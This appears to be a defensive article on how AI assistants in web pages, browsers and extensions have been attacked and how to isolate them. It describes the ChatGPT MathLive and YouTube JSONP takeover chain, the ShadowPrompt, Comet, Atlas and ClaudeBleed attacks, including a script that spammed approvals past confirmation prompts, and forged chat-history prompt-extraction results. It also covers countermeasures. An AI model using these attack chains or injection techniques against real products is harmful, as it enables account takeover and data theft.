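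The page still has to check the contents of each message. The chart's code could misuse the port or pass it on to another window. A script injected into the account page could replace `MessageChannel` before the page uses it and keep both ports. A private channel also does not secure other listeners in the page, such as one from a library the developers have forgotten about.

### From a maths keyboard to the ChatGPT page

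In October 2026, researchers at the security firm Parameter found a way into other people's ChatGPT accounts through a listener of that kind. *Do the Math* (Goyal, 2026) describes the attack, which used a link to a shared conversation.

ChatGPT can turn a block of HTML in a reply into a small working web page, called a preview. A preview can run any JavaScript, so ChatGPT puts it in a restricted frame at a different web address. The researchers first confirmed that code in the preview could not read the ChatGPT page around it, then looked for anything in that page that would accept a message.

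The same conversation contained an interactive graph. To support it, ChatGPT loaded MathLive, a library for entering and displaying mathematics. MathLive added a listener to the main ChatGPT page for messages about its on-screen keyboard.

The listener accepted messages from any origin because MathLive's setting for checking senders was `"none"`. According to the release history on Socket's *mathlive* page, this had been the default since version 0.90.8 in March 2023. Earlier versions accepted only messages from the page's own origin by default. The release notes called the older setting more secure and explained how to restore it.

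The preview sent two messages. The first replaced one of the keyboard's layouts, which can contain HTML, with one containing the researchers' markup. The second made MathLive show the keyboard. MathLive then put the layout into a string of HTML and assigned that string to `innerHTML` in the main page.

On the way, the string passed through the `createHTML` function, which marked it as trusted and returned the markup unchanged. MathLive leaves cleaning the HTML to the site, and its *Mathfield Changelog* had reminded developers in February 2025 to consider connecting this function to a sanitiser such as DOMPurify if they handled untrusted input.

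The unchanged default had already contributed to another flaw. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-54705* (2026) explains that MathLive did not encode ordinary text inside a formula, so markup in that text could run script. On a chat page, such a formula could come from a model's reply. MathLive fixed the flaw in June 2026.

### From inserted HTML to running code

The researchers could now add HTML to the ChatGPT page, but they couldn't yet run script. Browsers do not run script tags inserted through `innerHTML`, and ChatGPT's Content Security Policy (CSP) blocked inline code.

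They inserted a `srcdoc` frame because script tags run in its new document. The frame had no `sandbox` attribute, so its document had the `chatgpt.com` origin and its scripts could reach the main page.

The CSP still blocked inline code inside the new frame, but it allowed scripts from YouTube. One YouTube address, which supplies information for embedding videos, supports JSONP, so it takes a function name from the request. YouTube returned an error if the name was invalid, but it put the text from the request at the start of that response and sent it all as JavaScript. The browser accepted the response as a script from a permitted host and ran the researchers' code as part of `chatgpt.com`.

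The original preview stayed in its restricted frame throughout. MathLive created the new frame from inside the main page, so the researchers did not need to break the browser's separation of origins.

According to KIberblick's *ChatGPT* (2026), an article on a German site about AI, the code then read the victim's session token, requested the list of recent chats, loaded a private one and sent an excerpt to an outside server. Willison (2026), in *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts*, explains that the code sent the data out through an image reference. Goyal describes the result as essentially an account takeover, since the code could call ChatGPT's own interfaces as the victim.

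### Making one link enough

The first working version sent its messages from a ChatGPT app that the researchers controlled. It was not a convincing attack on strangers, because a victim would have had to connect or use that app.

The researchers next put the code in an HTML file attached to a conversation. ChatGPT opened the file in the same kind of preview, and the preview could send the messages. But when they shared the conversation publicly, the shared copy included the attachment but not the graph. Without the graph, ChatGPT did not load MathLive, so the page had no listener for the messages.

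They solved this by putting a graph and a preview written by the assistant in one ordinary conversation. Both remained when the conversation was shared. The attacker could then email the link to the shared conversation or post it anywhere, and a victim who was signed in to ChatGPT only had to open it.

In the most reliable version, the victim also had to click the "Preview" button. The researchers later got ChatGPT to open the preview automatically. They reproduced the automatic version three times in a separate account, and their test alert appeared after about 4.5 seconds.

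The model had written the preview earlier, in the attacker's conversation. The attack didn't use the victim's assistant, and the victim didn't have to ask it anything. Training the model to ignore instructions in outside text would therefore not have protected the victim.

### The report and the fixes

OpenAI closed the hole eight days after Parameter reported it:

| Date in 2026 | Event |
|---|---|
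| October 13 | Parameter finds the path from a MathLive message to HTML in ChatGPT's live code. |
| October 18 | Parameter reports the flaw through OpenAI's programme for paying outside researchers. |
| October 21 | OpenAI reproduces the attack and raises its priority from P2 to P1. |
| October 22–23 | OpenAI fixes one version of the web interface and changes the CSP to block part of the chain. |
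| October 26 | OpenAI has fixed both versions. It closes the report and pays $5,000. |
| October 28 | Parameter publishes its account. |
| October 31 | MathLive releases version 0.111.2. |

Willison called the payment "a bit cheap for a vulnerability this serious".

No one is known to have used the flaw against real users. The news site Infobae reports that Parameter found no evidence of such attacks and tested the attack only between its own accounts. KIberblick, however, notes that Parameter does not say whether anyone had exploited the flaw earlier. Parameter's finding would be weak evidence in any case, because an outside firm cannot normally search the server logs where an earlier attack might have left traces.

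Since version 0.111.2, MathLive's keyboard has accepted messages only from its own origin unless a developer permits others. Sites that use an older version with the open default need to update the library or change the setting. The risk is greatest for sites that also display untrusted content in frames, as ChatGPT does.

### Which controls would have broken the chain

Which other defences would have stopped the attack is a matter of analysis, not of test results, but the browser's rules give fairly clear answers:

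| Step in the attack | Possible control | Would it have stopped the attack? |
|---|---|---|
| The preview sends MathLive a message | Accepting messages only from the page's own origin | Yes |
| MathLive inserts the HTML | Trusted Types, with MathLive's `createHTML` as it was | No |
| MathLive inserts the HTML | DOMPurify inside `createHTML` | Yes, with its default settings |
| YouTube's response runs as a script | A nonce policy without a list of hosts | Yes |
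| The code requests private chats | A separate origin for shared conversations | Yes for the shared link, but not for the version with an app |
| Private text leaves in an image address | Allowing images only from the site's own origin | It would have closed only this way out |

#### Checking the sender

The sender check would have been the easiest control to add, since MathLive already had a setting for it, but it was hard to know that the listener existed. OpenAI's developers could have reviewed every listener they had written without finding this one. It also appeared only after ChatGPT had loaded a graph, so testing an empty chat page would not have revealed it.

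Checking the format of the message would not have helped much, because the researchers sent a keyboard layout in the form that MathLive expected, and HTML was a normal part of a layout.

#### Cleaning the HTML

Trusted Types would have let the markup through on any site that permitted MathLive's policy, because MathLive's function had marked the string as trusted. If a site had left the policy off its list, the browser would have blocked the attack, but the keyboard would probably have broken too.

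DOMPurify removes frames unless a site specifically allows them, so it would have removed the one the researchers needed. `setHTML()` would have done the same. Either could have removed markup that the real keyboard uses, so the developers would have had to test it before using it.

KIberblick's advice to run previews in a sandboxed frame on their own origin is good, but ChatGPT's previews already ran in a restricted frame at a separate address. The unsandboxed frame came from the researchers' markup, so OpenAI could not have fixed the problem by adding a sandbox attribute to its own code. It had to block the markup or remove the frame from it.

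#### Blocking the script

If the policy had relied on nonces and listed no permitted hosts, the browser would have refused the YouTube script because its tag had no nonce. The new frame inherited the main page's policy, so it would have applied there too. This assumes ChatGPT generated a new nonce for every page load, unlike the fixed one Imperva once found.

Adding nonces while keeping YouTube on the list would not have helped unless the policy also contained `'strict-dynamic'`. Removing only YouTube would have stopped the published bypass, but an attacker could then have searched the remaining hosts for a similar address.

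Even a perfect script policy would have left the attacker's HTML in the ChatGPT page, where it could have shown a false login form.

#### Separating the shared conversation

OpenAI could also serve shared conversations from a different domain where visitors are not signed in. The whole chain would still run there, but the code would have that domain's origin and could not read the visitor's private chats, as long as ChatGPT's servers refused requests from that origin. This would also protect visitors against flaws in other libraries.

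The separate domain is less convenient for visitors, who have to move the conversation to the main site to continue it. An attack hidden in the conversation could then run there when they open it. The separate domain also wouldn't have stopped the researchers' first version of the attack, which worked through an app and not a shared link.

Putting the graph in its own frame from another origin would have covered both versions. MathLive's listener and its use of `innerHTML` would then have been in a document that couldn't access the user's account. The graph and the chat would need to exchange a few messages, but they could do so over a private channel.

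#### Limiting what the code could send

A tighter `img-src` rule would have blocked an image request to an outside server, but the attacker's code could have sent the text out by navigating the page instead. The code could also have acted in the account through ChatGPT's own interfaces, which the page needs to contact.

### An assistant that sent its messages to anyone

Researchers have found unsafe uses of `postMessage` in other AI companies' products and elsewhere at OpenAI. While looking for ways to attack OpenAI's Atlas browser, Hacktron found that a message could inject a script into `forums.openai.com`. Researchers choose targets they expect to be weak or valuable, so these cases do not show what share of all listeners are unsafe.

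daily.dev, a site that collects articles for developers, summarises an attack on an AI assistant platform that it does not name. The platform used wildcard origins for both sending and receiving. An open listener lets a hostile page send false data or commands, as in the ChatGPT attack. Sending with a wildcard creates the opposite problem, because a hostile page can receive data intended for another one.

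The attack combined this mistake with two others. A prompt in a URL parameter made the assistant display HTML in a sandboxed frame. The attacker could then inject script into that frame and escape the sandbox with `window.name`. This property holds a short label for a window, but a script can set it to any text. The text can survive when the window moves to a page from another origin, so one page can pass data or code to the next.

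The attacker's script also followed the reference from its own window to the window that had opened it, and from there to the frames inside. The browser lets pages from different origins follow these references to exchange messages, but not read each other's contents. Because the platform did not restrict who received its messages, the attacker could keep collecting private data from conversations with the assistant.

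The recommended fixes include checking the sender's origin, naming an exact target origin, and cleaning HTML with DOMPurify. Another is the `Cross-Origin-Opener-Policy` header, which can make the browser cut the references between a site's page and windows from other origins. An attacker who opens the page in a new window then cannot send it messages or reach its frames. The header would not have helped ChatGPT, because the hostile preview was a frame inside the page, and the browser does not cut the reference between a page and its own frames.

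## Extensions and browsers that take orders from a website

A script that an attacker injects into a bank's page can read the customer's bank data, but the same-origin policy stops the script from reading their email. An assistant that works across websites needs broader access, so its maker builds it into a browser extension or the browser itself. Some makers also let their own websites send the assistant commands. An attacker who injects a script into one of those websites can then use the assistant to reach every site where the user is signed in.

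In browsers built on Chromium, the open-source code behind Chrome, an extension has a manifest, a file that can list which websites may send it messages. Perplexity's Comet browser runs most of its assistant in a built-in extension, whose manifest had this entry:

```json
"externally_connectable": {
  "matches": ["https://*.perplexity.ai/*"]
}
```

The first asterisk stands for any subdomain and the second for any page on it. A script on a matching page can send the extension a message, and the extension's code determines how it responds. If the message is an instruction to open and read a page, the extension can do so with the user's cookies.

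OpenAI's Atlas browser gave OpenAI's websites access to Mojo, Chromium's internal messaging system. Mojo normally serves only the browser's own pages, such as its settings.

### Three products that trusted every subdomain

Researchers took over parts of three assistants by finding a script flaw somewhere on the maker's domain:

| Product | Addresses it trusted | Where the researchers ran script | Addresses it trusted after the fix |
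|---|---|---|---|
| Claude's Chrome extension | `*.claude.ai` | An old CAPTCHA component | `claude.ai` only |
| Comet | `*.perplexity.ai` | A site for a fellowship programme | Not reported |
| Atlas | `*.chatgpt.com` and `*.openai.com` | A discussion forum | `*.chatgpt.com` |

#### Claude's extension

The security firm Koi called its attack ShadowPrompt. The extension accepted a message meant for a demonstration to new users and passed its text to Claude as if the user had written it.

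Anthropic used CAPTCHAs, puzzles meant to tell people from bots, made by Arkose Labs and served from a subdomain of `claude.ai`. The address of one puzzle contained a version number, so the researcher tried lower numbers and found an old version still on the server. That version accepted messages from any website and inserted text from them as live HTML.

A hostile website could load the old puzzle in an invisible frame and send it markup. The script in that markup ran on a subdomain the extension trusted, so it could give Claude any instruction. The victim only had to visit the site. In Koi's demonstration, the attacker obtained a lasting access token for the victim's Gmail, Google Drive and contacts.

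Koi reported the flaw on December 26, 2025. On January 15, 2026, Anthropic released a version that accepts messages only from exactly `https://claude.ai`. People with older versions were still exposed, so Arkose Labs also had to repair the puzzle, which it did on February 19.

#### Comet

Hacktron's *Securing Perplexity's AI Browser from a One-Click UXSS* (2025) describes an attack that began on the fellowship site's logout page. The page took its redirect address from its own URL and accepted a `javascript:` address. A firewall blocked the obvious attempts, but one researcher found a form of the code that it missed.

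The script could then call functions in Comet's extension. One function, apparently left over from testing, returned the contents of any address, including files on the user's computer. Two others opened Gmail in a tab and read it. Another started the assistant on a task of the attacker's choice, and the researchers used it to change a Perplexity username. They also tried to run programs on the computer but failed.

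Perplexity released a fix on August 20, 2025, a day after the report.

Another firm, SquareX, later claimed that a hidden interface in Comet could run programs on the user's computer. According to SecurityWeek, an attacker would first have to take over one of Comet's extensions through a script flaw or a network attack, or break into Perplexity's systems. Perplexity called the claim "entirely false", saying that the interface requires developer mode, the user's consent and a manual installation, according to TechRadar's *Perplexity responds to Comet browser vulnerability claims, argues "fake news"*. SquareX replied that Perplexity had quietly changed Comet after seeing its demonstration.

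#### Atlas

Hacktron found an unsafe message listener in OpenAI's forum while looking for a way into Atlas. The forum used it only for signed-in visitors, so the attacker's page first had to sign the victim's browser in with a forged login request.

From the forum, the script could open and close tabs, send them to other addresses and search the browsing history. The researchers could not get it to run code in other sites or start Atlas's agent, but it could list the full address of every open tab in real time, which was enough to take over accounts elsewhere. During an OAuth sign-in, a service often returns a one-time code in the address. Hacktron's page started a sign-in to GitHub, read the code from the list of tabs and used it to access the victim's repositories.

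OpenAI fixed the flaw on October 23, 2025, the day it received the report. NVD's *CVE-2026-11326 Detail* (2026), the flaw's entry in the US government's vulnerability database, gives it a medium severity of 6.0 out of 10. The entry mentions browsing history and control of tabs but not the sign-in codes, so it understates what Hacktron demonstrated.

### Why a wildcard lets in so much

The number of trusted domains is a poor guide to the risk. Atlas trusted two and the other products one each, but a wildcard covers every subdomain the company has now and every one it creates later. Companies put forums, event pages and other firms' services on subdomains, partly because the same-origin policy keeps a flaw there from affecting the main site. The wildcard removes that protection. The people who ran Perplexity's fellowship site had little reason to think that the security of users' email depended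 on its logout page.

An attacker needs only one weak subdomain and can take their time finding it. Hacktron searched OpenAI's sites for several days before finding the flaw in the forum.

The Cloud Security Alliance, an industry group, points out that third-party code on a subdomain and old builds that nobody has deleted both inherit the domain's trust. Arkose Labs' current puzzle did not have the flaw, so a review of the pages Anthropic was using would have missed it.

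OpenAI's fix excluded the forum but kept a wildcard for `chatgpt.com`. The October 2026 attack through MathLive ran script on `chatgpt.com` itself. If Atlas still trusted that address at the time, the script could have called the browser's functions for anyone who opened the attacker's link in Atlas.

The safest address to trust is therefore one used only to control the assistant. Its page would display no replies or shared conversations and load no third-party scripts. The ordinary chat page is a poor choice even if the list contains its exact address.

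### When the exact origin is not enough

Claude's extension already trusted only `claude.ai` when LayerX, a browser security firm, reported another flaw in April 2026. The extension checked which origin a message came from, but the browser gave it no way to check which script on the page had sent the message. LayerX wrote a second extension, with no special permissions, that ran a script as part of the `claude.ai` page. This script could send Claude any prompt. The attack became known as ClaudeBleed.

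Claude asked for confirmation before sensitive actions, but the script could keep sending "Yes, proceed" until Claude accepted. Some actions were still blocked, so LayerX changed a button's label from "Share" to "Request feedback" and told Claude to click it, which shared a file with an outsider.

According to The Hacker News (2026), Anthropic then changed the extension to accept only nine fixed tasks from the website, so a script on the page could no longer write its own prompt. Three of those tasks read the user's Gmail, latest Google document or calendar.

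A script in the `claude.ai` page could still start one of the nine tasks by faking a click. The extension waited for a click on a certain button in the page, but didn't check the `isTrusted` property, which distinguishes real clicks from scripted ones. Manifold Security reported this in May, and the code was unchanged in version 1.0.80 in July. Checking the property would stop a simple forged click but not clickjacking, which tricks the user into making a real one.

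A fixed task is much less useful to an attacker than a free-form prompt. The Gmail task displays its results in the extension's own panel, which the page cannot read. To get the data out, the attacker would need another step, such as emailing the victim hidden instructions for Claude to find.

### Approval outside the page

Anthropic first responded to ClaudeBleed in version 1.0.70 by making the extension ask for approval in its side panel. The panel is separate from the web page, so a script in the page cannot press its buttons. This fixes the weakness that let LayerX's script approve its own requests in the conversation.

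Users could turn the approvals off by choosing a mode called "Act without asking", and then the original attack worked again. Even when the user had chosen to approve each action, LayerX found a way to open a second panel in "Act without asking" mode.

The panel still had a related weakness in July: it skipped all permission checks if its own address contained a certain setting. Anthropic closed Manifold's report because only the extension could create that address, and only for tasks the user had already told it to run unattended. That was true at the time, but a later flaw that let a page influence the address would also remove the approval step. Manifold recommended that the panel always start in the mode that asks for permission.

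LayerX recommends tying each approval to one specific action and letting it work only once. The panel should also base its description of the action on what the assistant is about to send, since a page can put any label on a button.

### Other extensions on the assistant's page

Unlike most attacks on a trusted page, a hostile extension doesn't need a flaw in the website, because browsers allow extensions to change web pages. It can read the conversation, add its own script despite the page's Content Security Policy, and alter requests and responses between the page and the server. By altering responses, it can also remove the header that contains the policy.

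Chrome lets an extension with the right permission change the Gemini website in an ordinary tab. Chrome also loads that website in a panel beside the page, where it can take screenshots, read local files and use the camera. An extension should not be able to change the panel, but Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, found that it could. A victim only had to open the panel for the injected code to gain those powers. Google fixed the flaw (CVE-2026-0628) in January 2026.

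The problem also affected other companies' products. The Hacker News' *One Extension Could Hijack AI Assistants Across Chrome, Comet, Edge, Opera Neon* (2026) reported in September that a researcher had used one extension against five products, including Claude's extension. Clubic's *Une simple extension peut détourner votre IA et voler vos données* identifies the researcher as Gal Weizman of Forever Security and says the extension needed only permissions that ad blockers commonly have. The five products' makers have fixed the flaws, and Weizman knew of no real attacks.

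Clubic also says that all five attacks used a domain that the maker should have removed after internal testing. This fits the attack on Edge, which used a forgotten marketing page, but not Unit 42's account of the Chrome flaw, in which the extension altered the normal address of the Gemini app.

A website cannot prevent this kind of interference. Users and employers can remove extensions they don't need, and browser makers can block extensions from accessing any page that controls an assistant.

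### Old web flaws in a new form

The attacks so far used ordinary script flaws to give an assistant orders. Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* argues that assistants in browsers also recreate such flaws without any script. The security firm tested several products and compared its attacks with older ones:

| Older attack | Version that uses the assistant |
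|---|---|
| Reflected XSS | The user asks about a web page, and hidden text in it makes the assistant give a false answer. |
| Stored XSS | An Instagram message makes the assistant leak the user's contacts when the user asks for a summary. |
| Cross-site request forgery (a forged request sent with the user's cookie) | A hostile page makes the assistant open a private page on another site and pass on what it contains. |

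The newer attack in the last pair is worse than the older one, although Trail of Bits calls them functionally identical. An ordinary forged request may change something in the user's account, but the same-origin policy keeps the hostile site from reading the response. In the newer attack, the assistant can read the response and send it to the attacker.

The firm traces these attacks to poor isolation. Text from a hostile site and data from the user's accounts enter the same conversation, and the assistant can then send requests to other sites. Trail of Bits proposes extending the same-origin policy to that conversation, by keeping a list of every origin whose content has entered it:

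- With no origins on the list, the assistant may send requests anywhere.
- With one, it may send requests only to that origin.
- With more than one, it may send none, because nobody can tell which origin influenced the model.

The last rule would stop one site from stealing another's data. It would also stop an assistant from copying a shopping list from Gmail into an Amazon basket, which is the kind of work people want these products for. A simpler measure is to run the assistant in a separate browser where the user is not signed in, but the assistant can do even less there.

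The comparison with older flaws is limited because a site can encode text so that the browser never treats it as code, but language models have no equivalent, as Trail of Bits acknowledges. The older flaws also persisted on the web, and ordinary XSS was the way into Comet and Atlas.

The makers of the products Trail of Bits tested for this study declined to coordinate on disclosure, so the firm did not name them. Perplexity, by contrast, hired the firm to test Comet before launching it. Trail of Bits' *Using threat modeling and prompt injection to audit Comet* (2026) reports four prompt injection techniques that could take private data from Gmail. Perplexity published its own account of how it addressed them.

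Makers generally acknowledge the risk but do not accept that they should abandon the idea. Anthropic's *Piloting Claude for Chrome* calls browser-using AI inevitable because so much work happens in browsers, and says that trials with real users are needed to build better safeguards. In a note on that announcement, also titled *Piloting Claude for Chrome*, Willison (2025) expected the whole concept of such an extension to be "fatally flawed", though he gave Anthropic credit for devoting most of its post to the dangers.

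### How Chrome limits its agent

Google's approach to isolation is less strict than Trail of Bits' rule. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes a design that gives each task two sets of origins. The agent may read pages from either set, but may click and type only on pages from the second. Chrome does not show the model the content of frames from any other origin, such as embedded advertisements.

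The model that plans the task can propose a new origin, but a separate check decides whether the task needs it. That check never receives text from web pages, so an attacker cannot give it instructions directly. For the shopping list, Chrome could let the agent read Gmail and use Amazon while blocking it from the user's bank site.

A second model, the User Alignment Critic, reviews each action before it happens. It receives the user's goal and a description of the proposed action, but not the web content that led to it, and can veto actions that don't serve the goal. Chrome also restricts addresses written by the model to known public ones, which makes it harder to hide private data in an address.

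Chrome asks the user before the agent opens certain sensitive sites, such as those of banks, or signs in with a saved password. For purchases, payments and messages, Parker says only that the agent "will try to pause", because Chrome has to recognise such actions first.

The first version was simpler than the design, tracking only the origins on which the agent could act, without a separate set for reading. Google Cloud later described Chrome's auto browse feature as using the same combination of a critic and limits on origins. Parker says Google tests the defences with automated attacks but gives no success rates.

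### Limits within a single site

Restricting an agent by origin is a coarse limit, because a shop's product reviews and account settings usually have the same origin. An attacker could post a review that instructs the agent to change the user's password, and the agent could do so without leaving the permitted site. Two research systems set finer limits.

#### Checking requests

*CELLMATE* (Meng, Feng and colleagues, 2025) checks the HTTP requests that the browser sends to the server. Clicking the same spot on the screen may open an email or delete it, but the resulting request identifies the action more specifically. For example, a request to a shop's order address places an order.

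A site using CELLMATE publishes a list that matches its requests to actions, and rules such as "allow purchases up to a chosen amount". When the user sets a task, a language model selects the rules the task needs, using only the user's words. The user confirms the selection, and a browser extension then blocks any request those rules don't allow. A rule can also count requests, so that an agent with a $50 limit can't place two orders for $49.

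To test the blocking, the researchers assumed that an attacker already had full control of the agent. They wrote 12 scripts to steal access tokens, delete projects and do other damage on GitLab. CELLMATE blocked all 12. However, each attack needed an action that the rules forbade, so the test doesn't cover misuse of permitted actions. For example, an agent that may comment on an issue could still put a secret in the comment.

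Across 209 shopping, travel and software tasks, three leading models selected exactly the right rules more than 94% of the time in every category. They were less reliable at filling in details such as a spending limit, with 81% to 97% accuracy on shopping tasks. Pages took 7.25% longer to load with 100 entries in the site's list and 15% longer with 300.

The main obstacle is that each site has to write and maintain its list. The system also doesn't check messages sent over WebSockets, and it assumes that no other extension interferes with requests.

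#### Hiding parts of the page

*Prismata* (Villa and Tan, 2026) describes a system that works without help from websites. The system determines which parts of a page the agent may read and which buttons the agent may press.

For each button or link, a model receives only the user's task, the element's text and the elements that enclose it, so a hostile review elsewhere on the page cannot influence its decision. A second check works inwards from the outermost element and looks for signs of outside content, such as the heading "Reviews". It assigns a trust level to each layer before reading the next. Prismata then removes outside content that the task doesn't need and makes the rest read-only.

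This depends on hostile text rarely enclosing a useful button. In a sample of 90,408 pieces of outside content from real pages, only 1.2% contained something the agent could click or fill in. About 0.1% did so without an earlier sign that outside content was coming.

Villa and Tan tested the system with three kinds of hostile pop-up on copies of common types of website:

| Average result | Without Prismata | With Prismata |
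|---|---|---|
| Attack succeeded | 85.5% | 0.7% |
| Task completed under attack | 4.5% | 23.0% |
| Task completed with no attack | 29.9% | 26.6% |

The system greatly reduces successful attacks and only modestly reduces performance on ordinary tasks. But pop-ups are easy to separate from the task, and the agent performed poorly even without an attack. The system also cannot help when the agent must read the hostile content to do its task, as when a fake review persuades it to choose a product.

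#### When the request itself is false

Prismata assumes that no attacker can run script on the trusted site. CELLMATE and Chrome's critic also start from the user's request and judge later actions against it. In ShadowPrompt, the request came from the attacker. If such a prompt asked the assistant to forward an email, a critic that took it as the user's goal would find the action consistent with that goal.

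The same false request would lead CELLMATE to select the rules for sending mail. Its confirmation box could still stop the attack if the script could not reach the box and the user noticed they had never asked for an email.

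## Checks that do not depend on the page

A script that controls a page can write the user's prompts and press the page's buttons, but it cannot change the code on the site's server, the browser's own dialogs or the user's phone. Checks in those places can therefore still work when the attacker controls the whole page.

### Keeping the conversation on the server

A chat server needs the earlier messages to answer a new one. If it gets them from the browser, a script can rewrite them first. Kaya and colleagues found this weakness in eight of the 17 chatbot plugins they studied. Seven accepted forged developer and assistant messages, and one accepted only forged assistant messages. None of the eight showed the forgeries in the site owner's dashboard.

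The researchers first tested forged messages on 300 live chatbots that used the most popular plugin. A plain request for the system prompt worked on 1% of them. A forged message telling the model to reveal the prompt worked on 56% when it appeared to come from the developer and on 55% when it appeared to come from the assistant. The forged messages also contained extra instructions, which may explain part of the gap.

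A laboratory test made a fairer comparison. It put the same kind of hostile instructions either in the user's own message or in a forged one, and ran each combination ten times on 11 models from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google. The researchers report that forging made attacks three to eight times as successful, but the gain depended on the attacker's goal. These are the average success rates for all 11 models:

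| Attacker's goal | Developer's instructions | User's own message | Forged assistant message |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reveal the system prompt | Basic | 28% | 41% |
| Reveal the system prompt | Strict | 0% | 38% |
| Write program code | Basic | 10% | 59% |
| Write program code | Strict | 0% | 38% |
| Misuse a tool | Basic | 37% | 48% |
| Misuse a tool | Strict | 38% | 67% |

Strict instructions to refuse tasks outside the chatbot's role stopped the first two attacks when the attacker could write only as the user. Both attacks worked again when the attacker could also forge messages from sources other than the user.

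Protecting the chat history did not protect the tool, which posted notices to a company's internal chat. The attacker wanted the tool to post a link in a channel that the whole organisation could read. All three Gemini models posted the link every time, even without a forged message. The models date from 2024 and 2025, and newer ones may resist better, but a site that protects its chat history still has to protect its tools separately.

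The researchers told the plugins' developers about the forging flaw in October 2024. By December, the most popular plugin, used by about half of the affected sites, had moved its message handling to the server. The developer of the second most popular plugin said some customers' workflows depended on changing messages. That plugin still accepted forgeries but began to log a warning.

*Eurostar's Chatbot Goes Off the Rails, Security Firm Finds* (Willing, 2025) describes a flaw in how the train operator Eurostar tried to prevent forged messages. The browser sent the whole conversation with each question, and messages that had passed a content check carried a cryptographic signature. The server verified only the signature on the newest message, so a tester from the security firm Pen Test Partners could send a harmless new message and put hostile instructions in an older one. The chatbot then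 revealed its system prompt and the name of the underlying model.

The server also accepted made-up conversation and message IDs, and the page displayed HTML from replies without sanitizing it. The tester thought these flaws together might let one customer's markup run in another customer's chat, but did not test this. Eurostar has fixed the flaws.

mldangelo, in *Eurostar chatbot analysis*, objects that the test showed no access to other people's data and no unauthorised action. That is a fair description of the harm. City AM's *Eurostar’s new AI chatbot left customers exposed* reports that customer information stayed behind a login, which the chatbot could not get past. The same mistake would matter much more at a bank whose assistant can add payees.

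The simplest remedy is for the browser to send only the new message and a conversation ID. The server checks that the conversation belongs to the signed-in customer, loads the earlier messages from its own records and labels the new text as the user's. Kaya and colleagues also suggest signing each message with a secret that only the server knows. The server then has to check every signature. Each signature should cover the sender's role, the conversation and the message's position, because otherwise an attacker could move a genuine message to a place where it means something else.

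Neither remedy stops an injected script from sending a new message as the customer. The server will accept the message and save it in the conversation as if the customer had written it.

### Limiting what the assistant may do

Since the server cannot tell who wrote a message, it should limit what any message can achieve. Pen Test Partners advises giving a model only the tools, data and actions that it needs. The bank could set these limits:

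| Task | What the server enforces |
|---|---|
| Show recent payments | It reads only the signed-in customer's accounts, whatever account number the model supplies. |
| Add a payee | It saves a request that takes effect only after the customer approves it in the phone app. |
| Make a payment | It pays only approved payees, up to a daily limit. |
| Change the password or phone number | It gives the assistant no tool for this. |

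The server has to enforce these limits in ordinary code. Kaya and colleagues tried protecting their tools with better instructions, such as telling the model to use only the preconfigured channel. This cut successful attacks by 40–75%, but many still succeeded. If the tool's code had set the channel instead of letting the model choose it, an injected prompt could not have changed it.

Separating reading from writing makes the limits easier to check. The code that answers questions can use a read-only database account, and a smaller service with its own credentials can handle payments. A mistake in the question-answering code then cannot move money, though it can still reveal private data.

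Rate limits restrict how often an injected script can rephrase a prompt that the model has refused. In the test behind Quarkslab's *From prompt to pwned*, the security firm could send large numbers of prompts and study the model's behavior because there was no rate limit. A limit on messages does not help if the first attempt works, so the bank also needs limits on the number and total value of payments.

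The assistant should also have its own session, with a credential that works only for the chat and its tools. An attacker who steals this credential cannot use it to change the customer's password. SRLabs' *AI Security* says the easiest way into the AI systems the firm has tested was usually an ordinary mistake, such as a service account with too many rights or an identity token the assistant should not have held. SRLabs, which sells such tests, gives no figures to support this.

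A separate session for the assistant does little against a script in the bank's main account page. That script can bypass the assistant and use the customer's main session to call the bank's normal payment function. The bank must therefore require approval for a new payee however the payment is made, including through the old web form that the assistant was meant to replace.

### Why a button or a passkey is not enough

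In the earlier example of a €240 payment to a plumber, an injected script changed the payee on the way to the bank. The page may still show "Keller Plumbing, €240" above an "Approve" button. The server receives a request from the page to continue, but cannot determine whether the customer or the script approved the payment.

A passkey gives the bank stronger proof that the customer is present. It is a pair of cryptographic keys, and the private one stays on the customer's device or in their password manager. The bank sends a random value called a challenge. The device asks for a fingerprint, face scan or PIN, then signs the challenge with the private key, and the bank verifies the signature with the public key. An injected script cannot copy the private key or supply the fingerprint.

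But the customer may not know which payment the fingerprint approves. The device's prompt names the bank's website, while the payee and amount appear only on the page, which the script controls. In the plumbing example, the customer touches the sensor to pay Keller, but the bank receives a valid signature for the attacker's payment. Report URI's *Passkey Implementation Pitfalls* (2026) lists this kind of manipulation among the attacks still possible after a site adopts passkeys.

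Signing in with a passkey is not necessarily safe from code injected into the legitimate site, because the code can send the signed response to another server. Lundberg (2022) noted this in a change to the text of WebAuthn, the standard behind passkeys.

Report URI recommends putting the payment's details into the challenge, so that the signature covers them. This stops an attacker from using the signature for a different payment later. It does not solve the problem in the example, because the script can request a challenge for the attacker's payment from the start. The customer then produces a valid signature for payment details they have never seen.

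The bank also needs to protect the process of adding a new passkey. Report URI describes an attack in which an injected script shows the victim a browser session running on the attacker's computer and persuades them to approve a passkey there. The attacker can then sign in long after the bank has removed the script. The bank should confirm a new passkey, like a new payee, on a device the customer already uses.

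### Payment details in the browser's own window

W3C's *Secure Payment Confirmation* (2026), a draft standard, adds the missing display. The page gives the browser the payee and amount, and the browser shows them in its own window, which the page's scripts cannot alter. If the customer agrees, the passkey signs a record of what the browser showed. In a shortened form, the record for the plumber would look like this:

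```json
{
  "type": "payment.get",
  "challenge": "q7Vd…",
  "payment": {
    "payeeName": "Keller Plumbing",
    "total": { "currency": "EUR", "value": "240.00" }
  }
}
```

An injected script can still give the browser false details, so the bank has to compare the signed record with the order it received. In the draft's example, a dishonest shop tells the bank to expect $100 but has the browser show the customer $1. The signed record lists $1, so the bank can refuse the payment.

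The script in the plumbing example therefore has two choices, and both can fail:

| Method of approval | Payee the customer sees | What the bank can establish | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Button in the page | Keller Plumbing | The page sent an approval. | The attacker is paid. |
| Ordinary passkey | Keller Plumbing | The customer used the passkey. | The attacker is paid. |
| Browser's payment window, with the attacker's details | The attacker | The customer saw the real payee. | The customer can cancel. |
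| Browser's payment window, with the plumber's details | Keller Plumbing | The signed payee differs from the one in the order. | The bank refuses. |
| Bank's phone app | The attacker | The customer saw the real payee. | The customer can cancel. |

The bank also has to check several other fields. If it ignored the `type` field, for instance, an attacker might be able to use a payment approval to sign in to the customer's account.

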